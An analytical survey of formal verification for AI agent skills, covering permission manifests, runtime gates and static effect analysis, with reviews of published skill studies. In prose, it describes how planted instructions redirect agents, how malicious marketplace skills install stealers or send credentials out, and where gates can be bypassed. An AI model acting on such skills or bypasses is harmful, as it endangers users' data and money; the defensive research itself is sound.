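# Formal Verification of AI Agent Skills: Static Effect Analysis, Refinement Types and Bounded Model Checking

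## Agent skills, their permissions and the property to be proved

An agent skill is a folder of instructions, often with small programs, that an AI agent loads for one kind of task, such as filling in PDF forms or reviewing code. The agent consists of a large language model and a program that acts on the model's output by reading files, running commands or sending messages. Installing a skill leaves the model unchanged, but the agent follows the skill's instructions and runs its programs with whatever access the user has given the agent, so a carelessly written or malicious skill can do serious damage. Formal verification of a skill means proving, by mathematical analysis of its programs, that it stays within a list of permissions fixed before it runs.

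Alfredo Metere, of Metere Consulting, proposed a scheme for doing this in two papers in May 2026. *Skills as Verifiable Artifacts* (2026) specifies how a skill should declare its permissions and how the agent's software should enforce them. *Methods for Formal Verification of Agent Skills* (2026) adds three techniques for proving that the declaration is true. Both papers start from the observation that a signature identifies who endorsed a skill but is no evidence of how the skill behaves. If nobody has checked the behaviour, the software has to ask a human before every irreversible action, and Metere expects people who receive that many requests to approve them all without reading them.

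### What a skill contains and how an agent loads it

Agent Skills' *Specification*, which defines the common format for skills, requires only one file, SKILL.md. The file begins with a short block of metadata, followed by Markdown instructions that may take any form. The only required metadata fields are a name of at most 64 characters and a description of at most 1,024. An author may add separate folders for scripts, reference documents and assets such as templates.

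Nothing here requires an author to list what the skill will do to the user's machine. The closest thing is an optional, experimental field called `allowed-tools`. An entry such as `Bash(git:*) Read` names tools that the agent may use without asking first, but does not limit the agent to those tools. *Beyond Maliciousness* (2026) reports that in at least one major agent, the field removes the confirmation prompts for the listed tools and leaves every other tool callable. A skill therefore works with ambient authority, the security term for access that a program has merely because of where it runs. *When Safe Skills Collide* (2026) notes that installed skills also share one session, so the agent has the combined capabilities of all of them.

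The runtime is the program that loads skills, passes text to the model and carries out the model's requests. Agent Skills' *How to add skills support to your agent* describes its work in stages. At the start of a session, the runtime scans the project folder and the user's home folder for directories that contain a SKILL.md file. It adds each skill's name and description to the model's input, which takes 50 to 100 tokens per skill. When the model matches a task to a description, or the user names a skill, the full instructions enter the conversation. Scripts and reference files stay on disk until the instructions require them.

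The guide favours compatibility over strictness. It recommends that a runtime log a warning but still load a skill whose name breaks the rules. It also mentions, as an advantage of rereading the instructions at each activation, that the runtime picks up any changes to the file. This is a hazard for verification, because a proof about a skill no longer applies once its text changes. The guide does suggest one trust check, which is to load skills from a newly cloned repository only if the user has marked the project folder as trusted.

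### From the model's request to the host system

A language model only produces text. To act, it outputs a structured request, which another program may or may not carry out. Anthropic's *How tool use works* describes this exchange for Claude models. The model's reply contains a tool's name and arguments, the application runs the operation and returns the result, and the loop repeats until a reply contains no tool request.

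Metere calls the request an envelope, which consists of an operation, its arguments and the model's stated reason. The runtime's gate is the decision procedure that admits the envelope, denies it or refers it to a human. The runtime's dispatch function turns an admitted envelope into a real call to the host system, such as one to the operating system's routine for deleting a file.

Before an action that cannot be undone, the runtime logs the request and consults a broker, a component that the operator chose at installation and that answers "approve" or "deny". The runtime logs the answer with the broker's identity, carries out the action if approved, and logs success or failure. A shared identifier links these records. The broker may ask a person or a remote service, apply a written policy from a file the model cannot reach, or refuse every request.

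According to Anthropic's documentation of skills, Claude runs a bundled script through a command shell and receives only the script's output. The code never enters the model's context. The gate receives an envelope containing a request to run `fetch.py`, but the envelope does not show what the script then does with the network or the disk.

### Why the script side and the model side need different methods

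A skill has effects through the programs it ships (the script side) and through the tool calls that the language model makes after reading the skill's instructions (the model side). Metere separates the two because an analyst has different material to examine in each.

A script is a fixed text in a language with known rules. Its behaviour may vary with its input, the time of day or a web server's reply, but the text limits what it can do, and an analyser can read the text. The model has no such text. Its next envelope depends on billions of learned weights, the whole conversation so far and random sampling, and a sentence in a fetched web page may change it. Metere therefore treats the model as an adversary that may send any envelope, instead of trying to predict it, and places the guarantee at the one point every envelope must pass through.

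Neither approach can replace the other. Analysing every script does not reveal a payment request that the model generates on its own. An envelope check can confirm that the skill may invoke a tool but miss that the tool's script contacts an unapproved host.

### A vocabulary of capabilities

We can compare what a skill does with what it is permitted to do only if both are described in the same terms. Metere uses capabilities for both. A capability is a named kind of effect on the world, usually with a target. The basic vocabulary has nine capabilities.

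| Capability | Effect |
|---|---|
| `net.egress(host)` | contacting a host over the network |
| `fs.read(path)` | reading files under a path |
| `fs.write.rev(path)` | writing in a way the runtime can roll back |
| `fs.write.irrev(path)` | deleting, overwriting or truncating files |
| `tool.invoke(name)` | calling a tool registered with the runtime |
| `spawn.proc(cmd)` | starting an external process |
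| `publish(channel, …)` | posting to an external channel |
| `pay(token, amount)` | transferring money or other fungible value |
| `mutate.schema(target)` | migrating a database or configuration schema |

Much of the design depends on having separate entries for reversible and irreversible file writes, because only irreversible actions need approval. A write is reversible if it goes through the runtime's transaction buffer, which holds the change in memory until it commits or rolls back, and irreversible if it bypasses the buffer. The runtime can tell which path a write took without inspecting the disk. A script that opens and overwrites a file by itself therefore performs an irreversible write, even if the file is harmless.

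Other papers use different lists of capabilities. The eight in *When Safe Skills Collide* include reading environment variables, accessing credentials and accepting incoming network connections, none of which has its own entry among Metere's nine. This gap matters because programs commonly keep passwords in environment variables. *SkillGuard* (2026), which models its declarations on those of Android apps, covers devices such as the microphone, as well as the agent's own subagents and settings files. Metere calls the nine a minimum and lets a runtime add more, but a proof that a skill stays within its permissions can only cover effects that the vocabulary includes.

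### The manifest

The declaration sits in a manifest, the signed description of a skill. Formally, Metere defines a skill as a triple (*M*, content, σ), where *M* is the manifest, the content is SKILL.md with its scripts, and σ is a digital signature over both. The manifest has five compulsory fields:

- `label`, a confidentiality marking in the style of military classification, with a rank, a set of compartments and a list of permitted recipients;
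- `caps`, the capabilities the skill declares, which form the declared set *D*;
- `signer`, the identifier of the key that signed the skill;
- `version`, a number that only goes up, so that nobody can slip an old signed version back in;
- `verification`, the level of checking the skill has passed.

Before it reads any outside input, the runtime parses the manifest, looks up the signer in a locked list of trusted keys, verifies the signature, and compares the label with the clearances of both signer and user. It also checks that the signer is authorized to vouch for the stated level of verification. An error at any step stops the load, which is much stricter than the Agent Skills guide. Once loaded, the skill is frozen for the session. The runtime treats any attempt by the agent to edit it as an irreversible action that needs approval, and the edited skill must be verified again before the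 next session.

*Harnessing Agent Skills* (2026) warns against treating a skill's statement of what it needs as a grant of permission. The runtime's own policy should decide each use of a capability, with the skill's declaration as one input. Metere's manifest states what the skill needs, but at the higher levels of verification it also serves as a standing approval.

### Four levels of verification and the approvals they remove

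Every skill starts as unverified. At that level, its manifest gives it no privileges, and every irreversible call requires approval, whether or not the author declared it. The table shows how the other levels relax these rules.

| Level | Evidence behind it | Irreversible call inside *D* | Irreversible call outside *D* |
|---|---|---|---|
| unverified | none | human approval | human approval |
| declared | a trusted signer has examined the skill and vouches for *D* | automatic approval, with a log entry | broker decides, perhaps by asking a human |
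| tested | the skill has also passed trial runs with agents primed to do damage | as for declared | as for declared |
| formal | a machine-checkable proof that behaviour stays within *D* | as for declared | as for declared |

Moving from unverified to declared removes every prompt for calls inside *D*, on the strength of one signer's professional reputation. The tested level removes no further prompts but adds a safeguard. Between rounds, the runtime checks that changes to the world match the logged actions one to one, and it aborts the session if they do not. The runtime behaves the same at the formal level as at the tested level, but a proof gives the operator a better reason to leave the prompts off. Metere therefore expects most skills to stay at the tested level, and would reserve the effort of proof for the few with high-impact capabilities such as `pay`, `mutate.schema` and `spawn.proc`.

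Metere's rules for calls outside *D* are not quite consistent. The definition of the vocabulary has the gate deny any undeclared capability, regardless of the skill's instructions. Under the gate's policy, the same call goes to the broker, and a human may then approve it. If a person can approve an undeclared payment, the skill's session can contain an effect outside *D* that no analysis of the scripts will prevent, so a guarantee at the formal level needs the stricter rule, under which the gate always denies the call.

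### Adversaries and assumptions

Metere considers three attackers. The first publishes a malicious skill in a public registry and waits for agents to install it. The second leaves the skill unchanged but plants instructions in a document that a benign skill has the agent read, which is called prompt injection. The third is the agent itself, which through error or manipulation writes a new skill, registers it and uses it. This may happen without anyone intending harm, but the runtime cannot distinguish it from a deliberate attack.

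The scheme's guarantees against these threats assume that the attacker has not obtained the operator's signing key, altered the runtime or tampered with the stored log. They also assume that the runtime's code does what its design prescribes. Metere states this last assumption explicitly and adds that the existing implementation has not been proved to satisfy it.

On the model side, the runtime must also be able to intercept every envelope before it reaches the host system. Metere holds that every runtime that adopts SKILL.md meets this condition, but Anthropic's documentation describes an exception. For web search, web fetching, code execution and tool search, Anthropic's servers run the operation and usually complete it before the application sees anything. A runtime that enables these tools receives a report of the calls when it is too late for a gate to refuse them.

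Scripts are even harder to intercept. *enclawed* (Metere, 2026), which describes the open-source program that implements the scheme, lists what the program's network guard misses. The guard runs inside the runtime's JavaScript process, so it misses connections from native modules and from separate processes such as the download tool `curl`. A Python or shell script that an agent starts is also a separate process. Unless the operator adds controls in the operating system, as Metere requires for classified settings, the operator has to rely on an analysis of the script's source done before it runs.

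### Traces and capability containment

The property to be proved concerns what happens in a session. Let *C* be the vocabulary of capability names and *V* the set of possible targets: hosts, paths, amounts and so on. Metere defines the trace of a session *s* as the sequence, in order of time,

τ(*s*) = *e*₁ *e*₂ … *e*ₖ, with each *e*ᵢ in *C* × *V*.

Each *e*ᵢ is a capability with its target. It stands either for an envelope from the model or for an effect of a script, and it carries a note of its origin and of the gate's decision. Write Π(τ) for the set of capability names that occur anywhere in the trace. A skill with declared set *D* has capability containment on the session *s* if and only if

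Π(τ(*s*)) ⊆ *D*.

In words, every capability that appears in the session is declared in the manifest. A skill may also declare capabilities it doesn't use. Metere regards this as less serious than using undeclared ones, because an operator can see the extra capabilities in the manifest.

Suppose a skill that reports exchange rates declares *D* = {`tool.invoke`, `net.egress`, `fs.read`}. In one session the trace runs as follows.

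1. `tool.invoke(fetch_rates)`, from the model, admitted
2. `net.egress(api.example.com)`, from the script
3. `fs.read(./budget.csv)`, from the model, admitted

All three names are in *D*, so containment holds. In another session the rates page contains a planted instruction, and the model follows it.

1. `tool.invoke(fetch_rates)`, from the model, admitted
2. `net.egress(api.example.com)`, from the script
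3. `pay(EUR, 200)`, from the model, denied

Containment fails, although no money moved, because the trace includes every envelope the model emits, in Metere's words "whether eventually executed or denied at the gate", and Π collects the names "regardless of origin or gate decision". Even a perfect gate does not by itself secure containment, because it can block a payment but cannot prevent the model from emitting a request for one. A gate can secure the weaker property that every *executed* effect lies within *D*, which is probably what most operators care about.

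The definition is lax in another respect. *D* is a set of names and Π discards the targets, so the first trace would still pass if the script had contacted `attacker.example`. Metere's own worked example attaches targets to the declared capabilities and compares those too. Any useful version of the property has to do the same, because otherwise permission to contact one host would be permission to contact any host. Even then, a skill that stays within *D* can do harm. If it may read the user's files and send data to a host, it can steal the files by sending them to that host, using only permitted actions.

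### Sound analysis and over-approximation

No finite number of trial runs can establish containment for every session, since the next run may take a path that none of the earlier ones took. Suppose the script behind `fetch_rates` has two lines:

```python
if len(sys.argv) > 9: os.remove("budget.csv")
requests.get("https://api.example.com/rates")
```

A tester who runs these lines with one argument sees only a network request, but with nine or more arguments they also delete a file. An analysis is sound if it never misses a behaviour of the kind it covers. A sound analysis of these lines therefore reports both `net.egress(api.example.com)` and `fs.write.irrev(budget.csv)`, even if no agent will ever supply nine arguments.

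Such a report is an over-approximation. Let *E*(*p*) be the set of effects that a program *p* can have, and *Ê*(*p*) the set that the analysis reports. The analysis is sound if *E*(*p*) ⊆ *Ê*(*p*). To prove that a script stays within its permissions *D*, it is then enough to show that *Ê*(*p*) ⊆ *D*. If *Ê*(*p*) goes beyond *D*, as it does here, the script may exceed its permissions or the analysis may only be imprecise, so someone has to check. Some imprecision is unavoidable because no algorithm can compute *E*(*p*) exactly for every program. An analyser can reduce the number of spurious effects it reports, but it must still include every effect in *E*(*p*).

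### The three methods

Metere applies a separate technique to each part of the problem. A static analysis of the kind just described covers the scripts. Dispatch has a refinement type, which is an ordinary programming type with a logical condition attached. Here the condition is that the envelope's capability is in *D*. Bounded model checking covers the gate and the log by searching every session up to a fixed length *K* for violations.

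| Method | Reads | Output | Covers |
|---|---|---|---|
| Static effect analysis | source code of the skill's scripts | an over-approximation of their effects, for comparison with *D* | script side |
| Refinement types | the runtime's dispatch function and *D* | a type checker's verdict that dispatch accepts only envelopes within *D* | model side |
| Bounded model checking | a model of the gate and the log, with *D* and *K* | a session in which log and world disagree, or the finding that none exists up to length *K* | the runtime's handling of whatever the model side sends |

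## What published skills declare and what they can do

Capability containment compares what a skill does with the set *D* declared in its manifest. Skills in the common format have no such manifest, so researchers comparing a published skill with its author's declaration use the `allowed-tools` field in its metadata, although it has a different purpose.

### The `allowed-tools` field

As of October 2026, the `allowed-tools` field is still experimental in Agent Skills' *Specification*. It pre-approves the tools it lists but doesn't restrict the others. In an example from Anthropic's documentation for Claude Code, its coding agent, a skill that commits changes to a code repository lists three git commands. To stop a skill from using a tool, the user has to add a deny rule to the agent's permission settings. The skill's author writes the list and can make it as broad as they like, so Anthropic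 advises users to review a repository's skills before trusting the repository.

Support for the field varies even among Anthropic's own products. The company says that the command-line version of Claude Code honours it, but the software kit for building other agents does not. *Harnessing Agent Skills* explains that Claude Code also has a `disallowed-tools` field, which removes tools for the turn that invokes the skill. This is a real restriction, but it isn't part of the specification, so other runtimes may ignore it.

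The specification's `compatibility` field can mention network access, but only in free text, which a program cannot reliably compare with code. Contributors have proposed new fields for credentials, capabilities, environment access and required permissions. All four proposals were open on 28 August 2026, according to *Beyond Maliciousness*, and the specification had adopted none of them by late October. The format's originator decides whether to adopt them. *Skills are infrastructure, and a new open-source artifact class*, from George Washington University's open-source office (GW OSPO), points out that the originator kept stewardship of the standard when it published it.

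### How many authors declare anything

Few skill authors use the field. *From Registry to Repository* (2026) examined software-engineering skills from the skills.sh registry and from GitHub projects. The field appeared in 14.95% of the 13,206 registry skills and 12.47% of the 16,244 project skills. Only 14.42% of the registry skills and 8.37% of the project skills had a `scripts` folder. Some skills may keep programs elsewhere, but these figures suggest that most contain no scripts to analyse and act only through the model's tool calls.

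SKILL.md itself can also contain commands. In Claude Code, an author can write a shell command between backticks after an exclamation mark, and the runtime executes it and inserts the output before the model reads the text. The model sends no envelope for this command, so a gate that examines only envelopes does not cover it. An analyser that opens only script files also misses it.

Authors of curated skills declare more, but their declarations may restrict little. In the library that *Scientific Agent Skills* (2026) describes, 100 of 163 skills use `allowed-tools`, and 94 of those 100 include a shell. An agent with an unrestricted shell can read and write files and contact the network, so a declaration that allows one rules out almost nothing.

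### Comparing declarations with contents

Ratnesh Pandey and colleagues made a larger comparison in *Beyond Maliciousness*, scanning 6,309 marketplace listings in July and August 2026. Of these, 3,947 came from skillsmp and 2,362 from ClawHub, which serves users of the OpenClaw assistant. They excluded the most popular skills and those that nobody installs, so their percentages do not describe either marketplace as a whole.

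The researchers used a language model, usually Claude Haiku 4.5, to read every file in each skill and label the capabilities for which it found evidence. They then sorted the 70 labels into eleven groups. Evidence of shell execution appeared in half the listings, file reading in 35%, file writing and network access in 31% each, and credential access in 13%.

Of the 6,061 listings with readable metadata, 770 declared at least one tool. Pandey and colleagues compared each declaration with the listing's inferred capabilities in the five classes that both can express. They excluded credentials and environment variables because `allowed-tools` has no terms for them.

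The table uses the names for possible outcomes from *SkillProbe* (2026), which presents an auditing system for skill marketplaces. *D* is the set of capabilities a skill declares, and *C* is the set its contents imply. The counts come from Pandey and colleagues.

| Outcome | Relation | Listings | Contained in *D*? |
|---|---|---|---|
| match | *C* = *D* | 166 | yes |
| over-declaration | *C* is a proper subset of *D* | 147 | yes |
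| under-declaration | *D* is a proper subset of *C* | 300 | no |
| mixed | each has something the other lacks | 157 | no |

A containment check would pass the 313 listings in the first two rows, about one in twenty of those with readable metadata. It would fail the other 457, or 59% of the listings that declare anything. Declarations are more common on ClawHub than on skillsmp (17.7% against 9.9%), but 88% of those on ClawHub omit something, compared with 31% on skillsmp. Declarations usually omit shell execution and network access. File reading is more often declared unnecessarily.

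All these counts depend on a language model's reading of the files, which is not a sound analysis. The model may overlook a capability, or infer one from a command that the instructions only quote as an example. Pandey and colleagues read 140 benign listings in full and found no missed threats. They rescanned 89 listings and got the same verdict 84% of the time. Both checks tested verdicts about malice, but the 59% depends on the capability labels, for which the researchers had no independent ground truth. Three of the five authors work for Metano Labs, which builds and operates the scanner.

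The researchers also had an agent run nearly every skill in a sandbox. Among the listings with declarations, 91 used at least one capability that the comparison covers, and 54 of those used one they had not declared. This agrees with the static result but adds little to it, because the agent used a shell even without the skill in a smaller set of control runs. The sandbox runs also missed a family of skills with a setup script that makes lasting changes to the agent's configuration. The agent never ran the script because no other file in those skills mentions it. An analyser that reads every shipped program would not miss it.

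Even a correctly identified omission may be deliberate. `allowed-tools` lists the tools that are pre-approved, so an author may leave out the shell because they want the user to approve each command. The 59% figure therefore doesn't measure how many authors would misdescribe their skills in a manifest meant to list everything.

### Why Android apps erred the other way

Earlier studies of Android apps, browser extensions and Alexa skills found that developers usually requested more permissions than they needed. Pandey and colleagues attribute the difference from agent skills to enforcement. Android blocks permissions an app has not requested, so developers soon notice an omission because it breaks the app, while an unnecessary request breaks nothing. Leaving a tool off a skill's `allowed-tools` causes at most an extra prompt.

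Metere's manifest would give skill authors the same incentive to over-declare that Android gave app developers. When a skill fails verification, its author can narrow what it does, but adding the missing capability to *D* is usually easier. Enforcement would then turn many under-declarations into over-declarations, which a containment check accepts by definition.

Metere therefore seems optimistic in treating over-declaration as the lesser fault, because an unneeded irreversible capability in *D* is also approved automatically from the "declared" level upwards. The existing field has the same problem on a smaller scale. Of the 770 listings that declare it, 304 pre-approve a class of tool that the skill doesn't appear to need.

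*SkillGuard* gives some idea of how much enforced declarations help. Its runtime denies any operation that nobody has explicitly authorized and asks the user about sensitive ones. The researchers tested it with three agents on skills containing planted malicious instructions. The share of successful attacks fell from 35.3% to 20.7% when the instructions blended into the skill's text, and from 36.7% to 18.0% when they were obvious. After analyzing the errors, the researchers recommend finer permissions, especially lists of allowed targets for high-risk operations.

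### Actions that the user's task does not need

Identifying an excessive permission requires a standard for what the skill should do, and *SkillScope* (Wu, Wang and colleagues, 2026) takes that standard from the user's request. It calls an action over-privileged if the request does not authorize it or if the task succeeds without it. For example, the deep-work skill records working sessions. When a user asks for a graph of the last seven days, the skill should read its records and draw the graph. Its instructions also direct the agent to send the report to a Telegram account and to collect the computer's identifiers, network settings and command history.

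*SkillScope* tests for such actions by running the skill with and without them:

1. Program analysis and a language model turn the instructions and scripts into a graph of actions. The model keeps those that don't clearly fit the skill's stated purpose.
2. For each remaining action, the model writes user requests that should lead the agent to perform it, and creates sample files where the task needs them.
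3. An agent carries out each request twice in an isolated environment, first with the original skill and then with the suspect action removed. If the action sits inside a script, the test may replace the function containing it with one that returns immediately.
4. The model compares the two runs. If the second still does what the user asked, the action was unnecessary. In a separate check, the model decides whether the request authorized the action.

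Wu and colleagues applied this to 68,312 skills, found suspicious actions in 8,328 and confirmed over-privilege in 6,590, or about one in ten of all the skills. Models make the judgments here too, but people checked a sample of 300 confirmed skills and upheld about 94% of them, after weighting. The definition is also strict, so a skill that makes a backup before editing a file could count as over-privileged because the edit succeeds without the backup.

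In 5,092 of the 6,590 confirmed skills, the excess came from the instructions alone, so an analysis of scripts would not have found it. A containment check would also often miss it. If deep-work's manifest declared the Telegram connection and access to the relevant files, all these actions would lie within *D*. *SkillScope* can flag them because it takes the user's request into account, whereas a containment proof must hold for every session, whatever the task.

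### Malicious skills on ClawHub

A malicious author writes both the skill and its declaration, so an accurate declaration is not evidence of good intent. Many capable skills are harmless. Among the listings that Pandey and colleagues rated high or critical for exposure, 1,306 were judged benign and 315 suspicious or malicious.

Koi (2026), a security company, audited all 2,857 skills then on ClawHub, a public marketplace, and found 341 malicious ones, 335 of them from a single campaign that it named ClawHavoc. By 16 February 2026, the marketplace had grown to more than 10,700 skills and Koi's count of malicious ones had reached 824. These are counts of listings, so they don't measure how many users installed the malicious skills or lost data.

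The ClawHavoc skills posed as ordinary tools such as video summarizers and cryptocurrency trackers. Their documentation listed a helper program under "Prerequisites" for the user to install first. On Windows the helper was a trojan that recorded keystrokes, and on macOS it was Atomic Stealer, which steals passwords, browser data and cryptocurrency wallets. The malware was hosted on outside servers, so an analysis of the skills' own scripts would not have found it.

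Only three of the 341 skills had the attack in shipped code. In two tools for a prediction market, hundreds of lines of working code surrounded a command that downloaded and ran a remote script. A supposed weather tool read the assistant's configuration file, which held credentials, and sent it to an outside server. A sound analysis of effects would report these operations, and each skill would fail the containment check unless its manifest declared them.

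For the other 338, the outcome depends on who runs the installation command. If the agent tries to run it, the agent has to send an envelope, which the gate can deny if *D* lacks `spawn.proc`. If the user pastes it into a terminal, nothing passes through the runtime and none of Metere's three methods applies.

ClawHub responded to the early reports by screening skills automatically. Unit 42, the threat-research team of the security company Palo Alto Networks, still found five malicious skills there between February and May 2026. Two of them reused the fake prerequisite. Another, letssendit, worked through its instructions alone. It had agents pool cryptocurrency in its operator's wallet, and the operator bought a new token cheaply before giving the agents their share. An author could declare `pay` for such a skill. Its payments would then satisfy containment, and if a trusted signer had endorsed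 the manifest, the runtime would approve them without asking the user.

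## Static effect analysis of a skill's scripts

Metere's static effect analysis computes *Ê*(*p*) for each bundled script *p* and compares it with *D*. It builds on two older ideas, using effect systems to write down a program's effects and abstract interpretation to compute them.

### Effect systems

A type describes the value an expression returns, but not what else the expression does. A function that returns the integer 5 has the same type as one that deletes a folder and then returns 5. Lucassen (1987), in *Types and Effects*, proposed languages in which every expression has an effect as well as a type. The effect describes which regions of memory the expression may read or change. A compiler can use this information to find parts of a program that can run in parallel because they do not interfere with one another. Metere follows the later version by Lucassen and Gifford (1988), in *Polymorphic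 Effect Systems*, but replaces regions of memory with hosts, file paths and other targets of capabilities.

Effects are hard to determine when programs pass procedures around as values. In the call `job(url)`, the variable `job` may hold any function that another part of the program put there. Lucassen found that existing analyses needed a complete map of which procedure calls which, which can only be approximate when procedures are values. Lucassen instead had programmers state the effects at certain points, so that the compiler could verify effects rather than estimate them. The compiler infers the remaining effects and checks that everything agrees.

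Java's checked exceptions are an effect system. A method that may fail with an input or output error has to handle the error or declare `throws IOException`, in which case the same rule applies to its callers. In *Lightweight Polymorphic Effects*, Rytz, Odersky and Haller called this the only effect system that a widespread industrial language had adopted, and blamed the lack of others on the wordiness of effect annotations. In *Polymorphic type region and effect inference*, Talpin and Jouvelot had the compiler work out types and effects.

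Python, JavaScript and shell scripts have no effect annotations. A skill's manifest is one annotation for the whole package, so the analyser has to estimate the effects of everything in the package.

### Abstract interpretation

The estimate comes from abstract interpretation, a theory that Cousot and Cousot (1977), in *Abstract interpretation*, introduced for analysing programs. The analyser executes the program on summaries, each of which stands for many possible values. The interval [1, 9] stands for the whole numbers from 1 to 9, and the pattern `*.example.com` for every host under that domain. Write γ(*a*) for the set of values that a summary *a* stands for. For each operation *f* in the language, the analyser has a transfer function *f̂*, which takes a summary of the input and returns a summary of the output. The transfer function is sound if

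*v* ∈ γ(*a*) implies *f*(*v*) ∈ γ(*f̂*(*a*)).

If *f* adds 1, then *f̂*([1, 9]) has to cover every number from 2 to 10. The interval [2, 10] is the best answer. The interval [0, 100] is sound but imprecise, and [2, 9] is unsound because it misses 10.

A loop may run any number of times, so the analyser cannot follow each pass separately. It applies the loop's transfer functions repeatedly, merges each result with the previous one, and stops when the summaries no longer change. For a counter that starts at 1, this produces [1, 1], [1, 2], [1, 3] and so on without end. Widening ends this sequence by replacing the growing upper limit with infinity, which gives the sound but imprecise result [1, ∞). Cousot and Cousot (2014) recall that the earliest analyses used intervals and widening, and that a second operation, narrowing, came later to improve the results. If the loop runs only while the counter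 is at most 50, narrowing can use that test to reduce [1, ∞) to [1, 50] inside the loop.

### The effect lattice

To track effects as well as values, Metere attaches a set of pairs to each point in a script. Each pair contains a capability and a summary of its target. The summaries are patterns for paths and hosts, intervals for numbers, and "anything" for other values. These sets form a lattice, which means they are ordered and any two of them have a smallest set that covers both.

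- The order, *X* ⊑ *Y*, holds if *Y* covers every effect that *X* covers.
- The join, *X* ⊔ *Y*, is the union of the two sets. It describes a program that may have the effects of either.
- Bottom, ⊥, is the empty set. A script that only does arithmetic has this effect.
- Top, ⊤, covers every capability with every target. The analyser uses it when it cannot tell what the program will do.

Metere defines the order as plain set inclusion, which is too strict if taken literally. The pair (`net.egress`, `api.example.com`) is not in the set {(`net.egress`, `*.example.com`)}, although the host matches the pattern. Metere compares *Ê*(*p*) with *C*_D, a translation of *D* into the analyser's terms, and this comparison works only if *C*_D also contains every narrower pattern. Metere also calls the lattice finite, but there are infinitely many path patterns, so repeated merging may never stop without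 widening. In a finite lattice, the analyser would need widening only to save time.

### The transfer functions

The most important transfer functions handle library calls, because a script affects the outside world mainly through its language's libraries. The analyser looks up each call in a table and fills in the effect's target from the summary of the argument. In Metere's table for Python, `requests.get(u)` produces the effect (`net.egress`, *û*), where *û* summarises the address. The call `open(p, 'w')`, which opens a file for writing and erases its contents, produces (`fs.write.irrev`, *p̂*).

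At a branch, the analyser usually cannot predict which way the test will go, so it follows both sides and joins the results. It handles loops with the repeated merging and widening described above.

Some programs generate code at run time and execute it, using constructs such as Python's `eval` and `exec`. The analyser cannot read this code in advance, so under Metere's rule a single reachable construct of this kind sets the whole program's effect to ⊤.

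A script may also start another program. If that program is one of the skill's own analysed scripts, the first script inherits its effects. Otherwise the child process counts as ⊤. This rule is severe for shell scripts, where ordinary commands such as `curl` and `rm` are external programs. A usable analyser for shell scripts therefore needs table entries for such commands, and must assume that `rm` runs the usual program on the user's machine.

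### A script analysed by hand

The following script downloads exchange rates page by page until the server returns an empty page. Before 6 a.m., it uses a backup server.

```python
1  import time, requests
2  host = "api.example.com"
3  if time.localtime().tm_hour < 6:
4      host = "backup.example.com"
5  page, text = 1, "start"
6  while text:
7      text = requests.get(f"https://{host}/rates?page={page}").text
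8      open(f"rates/{page}.csv", "w").write(text)
9      page = page + 1
```

The table gives the analyser's state after each line, with the two hosts shortened to *api* and *backup*.

| After line | Summaries of the variables | Effects so far |
|---|---|---|
| 1 | none | ⊥ |
| 2 | `host` = {*api*} | ⊥ |
| 3 | test unknown, so the analyser follows both branches | ⊥ |
| 4 | `host` = {*backup*} in this branch; after the join, {*api*, *backup*} | ⊥ |
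| 5 | `page` = [1, 1], `text` = "start" | ⊥ |
| 6, first pass | no change | ⊥ |
| 7 | `text` = any string | `net.egress` to *api* and *backup* |
| 8 | no change | adds `fs.write.irrev(rates/1.csv)` |
| 9 | `page` = [2, 2] | no change |
| 6, second pass | `page` = [1, 1] ⊔ [2, 2] = [1, 2], widened to [1, ∞) | no change |
| 7 | no change | no change |
| 8 | no change | the write now covers `rates/N.csv` for every *N* ≥ 1 |
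| 9 | `page` = [2, ∞) | no change |
| 6, third pass | `page` = [1, 1] ⊔ [2, ∞) = [1, ∞), as before, so the analysis stops | no change |

The result is

*Ê*(*p*) = {(`net.egress`, `api.example.com`), (`net.egress`, `backup.example.com`), (`fs.write.irrev`, `rates/N.csv`)}.

Suppose the manifest declares *D* = {`net.egress(api.example.com)`, `fs.write.irrev(./rates/)`}. The writes all fall under the declared folder, but the backup host is not in *D*, so the check fails. Adding the backup host to the manifest would make the script pass.

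An analyser that kept only one host pattern per variable would have merged the two names into `*.example.com`. The check would then fail even against a manifest that lists both hosts, because the pattern also covers hosts that the script never contacts.

This script also contradicts Metere's assumption that the exact set *E*(*p*) is finite and computable for mainstream scripting languages. The script has no limit on the number of different files it may write, because that depends on when the server returns an empty page. The theorem does not need the assumption, since an over-approximation of *E*(*p*) is enough.

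### The summarise-fetched-html example

Metere applies the method to a skill called summarise-fetched-html. Its manifest declares `net.egress(*.example.com)` and `fs.read(./.cache/)`. Its one Python script fetches a web page from that domain, saves it in the folder `./.cache/`, reads it back and summarises it. The analysis reports three effects:

| Inferred effect | In *D*? |
|---|---|
| `net.egress(*.example.com)` | yes |
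| `fs.read(./.cache/)` | yes |
| `fs.write.rev(./.cache/)` | no |

The skill's author declared reading from the cache but not writing to it. Metere says the operator can fix this by adding the write to the manifest or changing the script. In the example, the operator adds `fs.write.rev(./.cache/)`, and the skill passes. Metere describes catching such omissions as the method's most common practical benefit, because authors change scripts and forget to update the declarations.

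However, the third effect should be irreversible by Metere's own rules. The table of library effects maps `open(p, 'w')` to `fs.write.irrev`, whatever the folder. A script that opens a file directly also bypasses the transaction buffer that Metere requires for a reversible write. An analyser could report a reversible write only if the script called a runtime function for buffered writes and the table had an entry for that function.

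If the operator added the reversible write to the manifest, a correct analysis would still find `fs.write.irrev(./.cache/)` outside *D*, and the skill would fail again. For the unchanged script to pass, the manifest has to declare an irreversible capability, which the runtime then approves automatically. An operator who thinks the cache writes can be rolled back is granting more than they realise. Changing the script to keep the page in memory is safer, because it would then need neither the write nor the read, and the manifest could declare only the network permission.

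The reported host pattern also depends on where the web address comes from. If the model passes the address to the script as an argument, the analyser has no information about the host and has to report every host. It can report `*.example.com` only if the script fixes the domain or rejects addresses outside it with a test that the analyser can interpret. Many useful scripts take an address or file name from the model, so their authors would have to write such tests.

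The manifest has another omission, which an analysis of the script cannot find. To start the script, the model has to send an envelope that needs `tool.invoke` or `spawn.proc`, and the manifest declares neither. The first use of the script would therefore break capability containment.

### The soundness theorem

Metere states the guarantee as a theorem. If the analyser finds *Ê*(*p*) ⊆ *C*_D for every script *p* in the skill, then all their effects lie within *D*, on every run and every input. The part of any session's trace that comes from these scripts is therefore contained in *D*.

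The proof is by induction on the structure of the program. If each library call's table entry covers the call's real effects, and the rules for sequences, branches and loops preserve this coverage, then the final set covers the whole program. Constructs like `eval` don't break the proof, because they send the result to ⊤. A result that fits within *D* therefore shows that the script has no such constructs, or that no run can reach them.

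The logic is valid, but it rests on the assumption that every transfer function over-approximates. Whether this is true depends on the analyser, the language and the machine on which the script runs. It has to be established for each analyser, including the one in enclawed, which searches the source for text patterns instead of computing abstract states.

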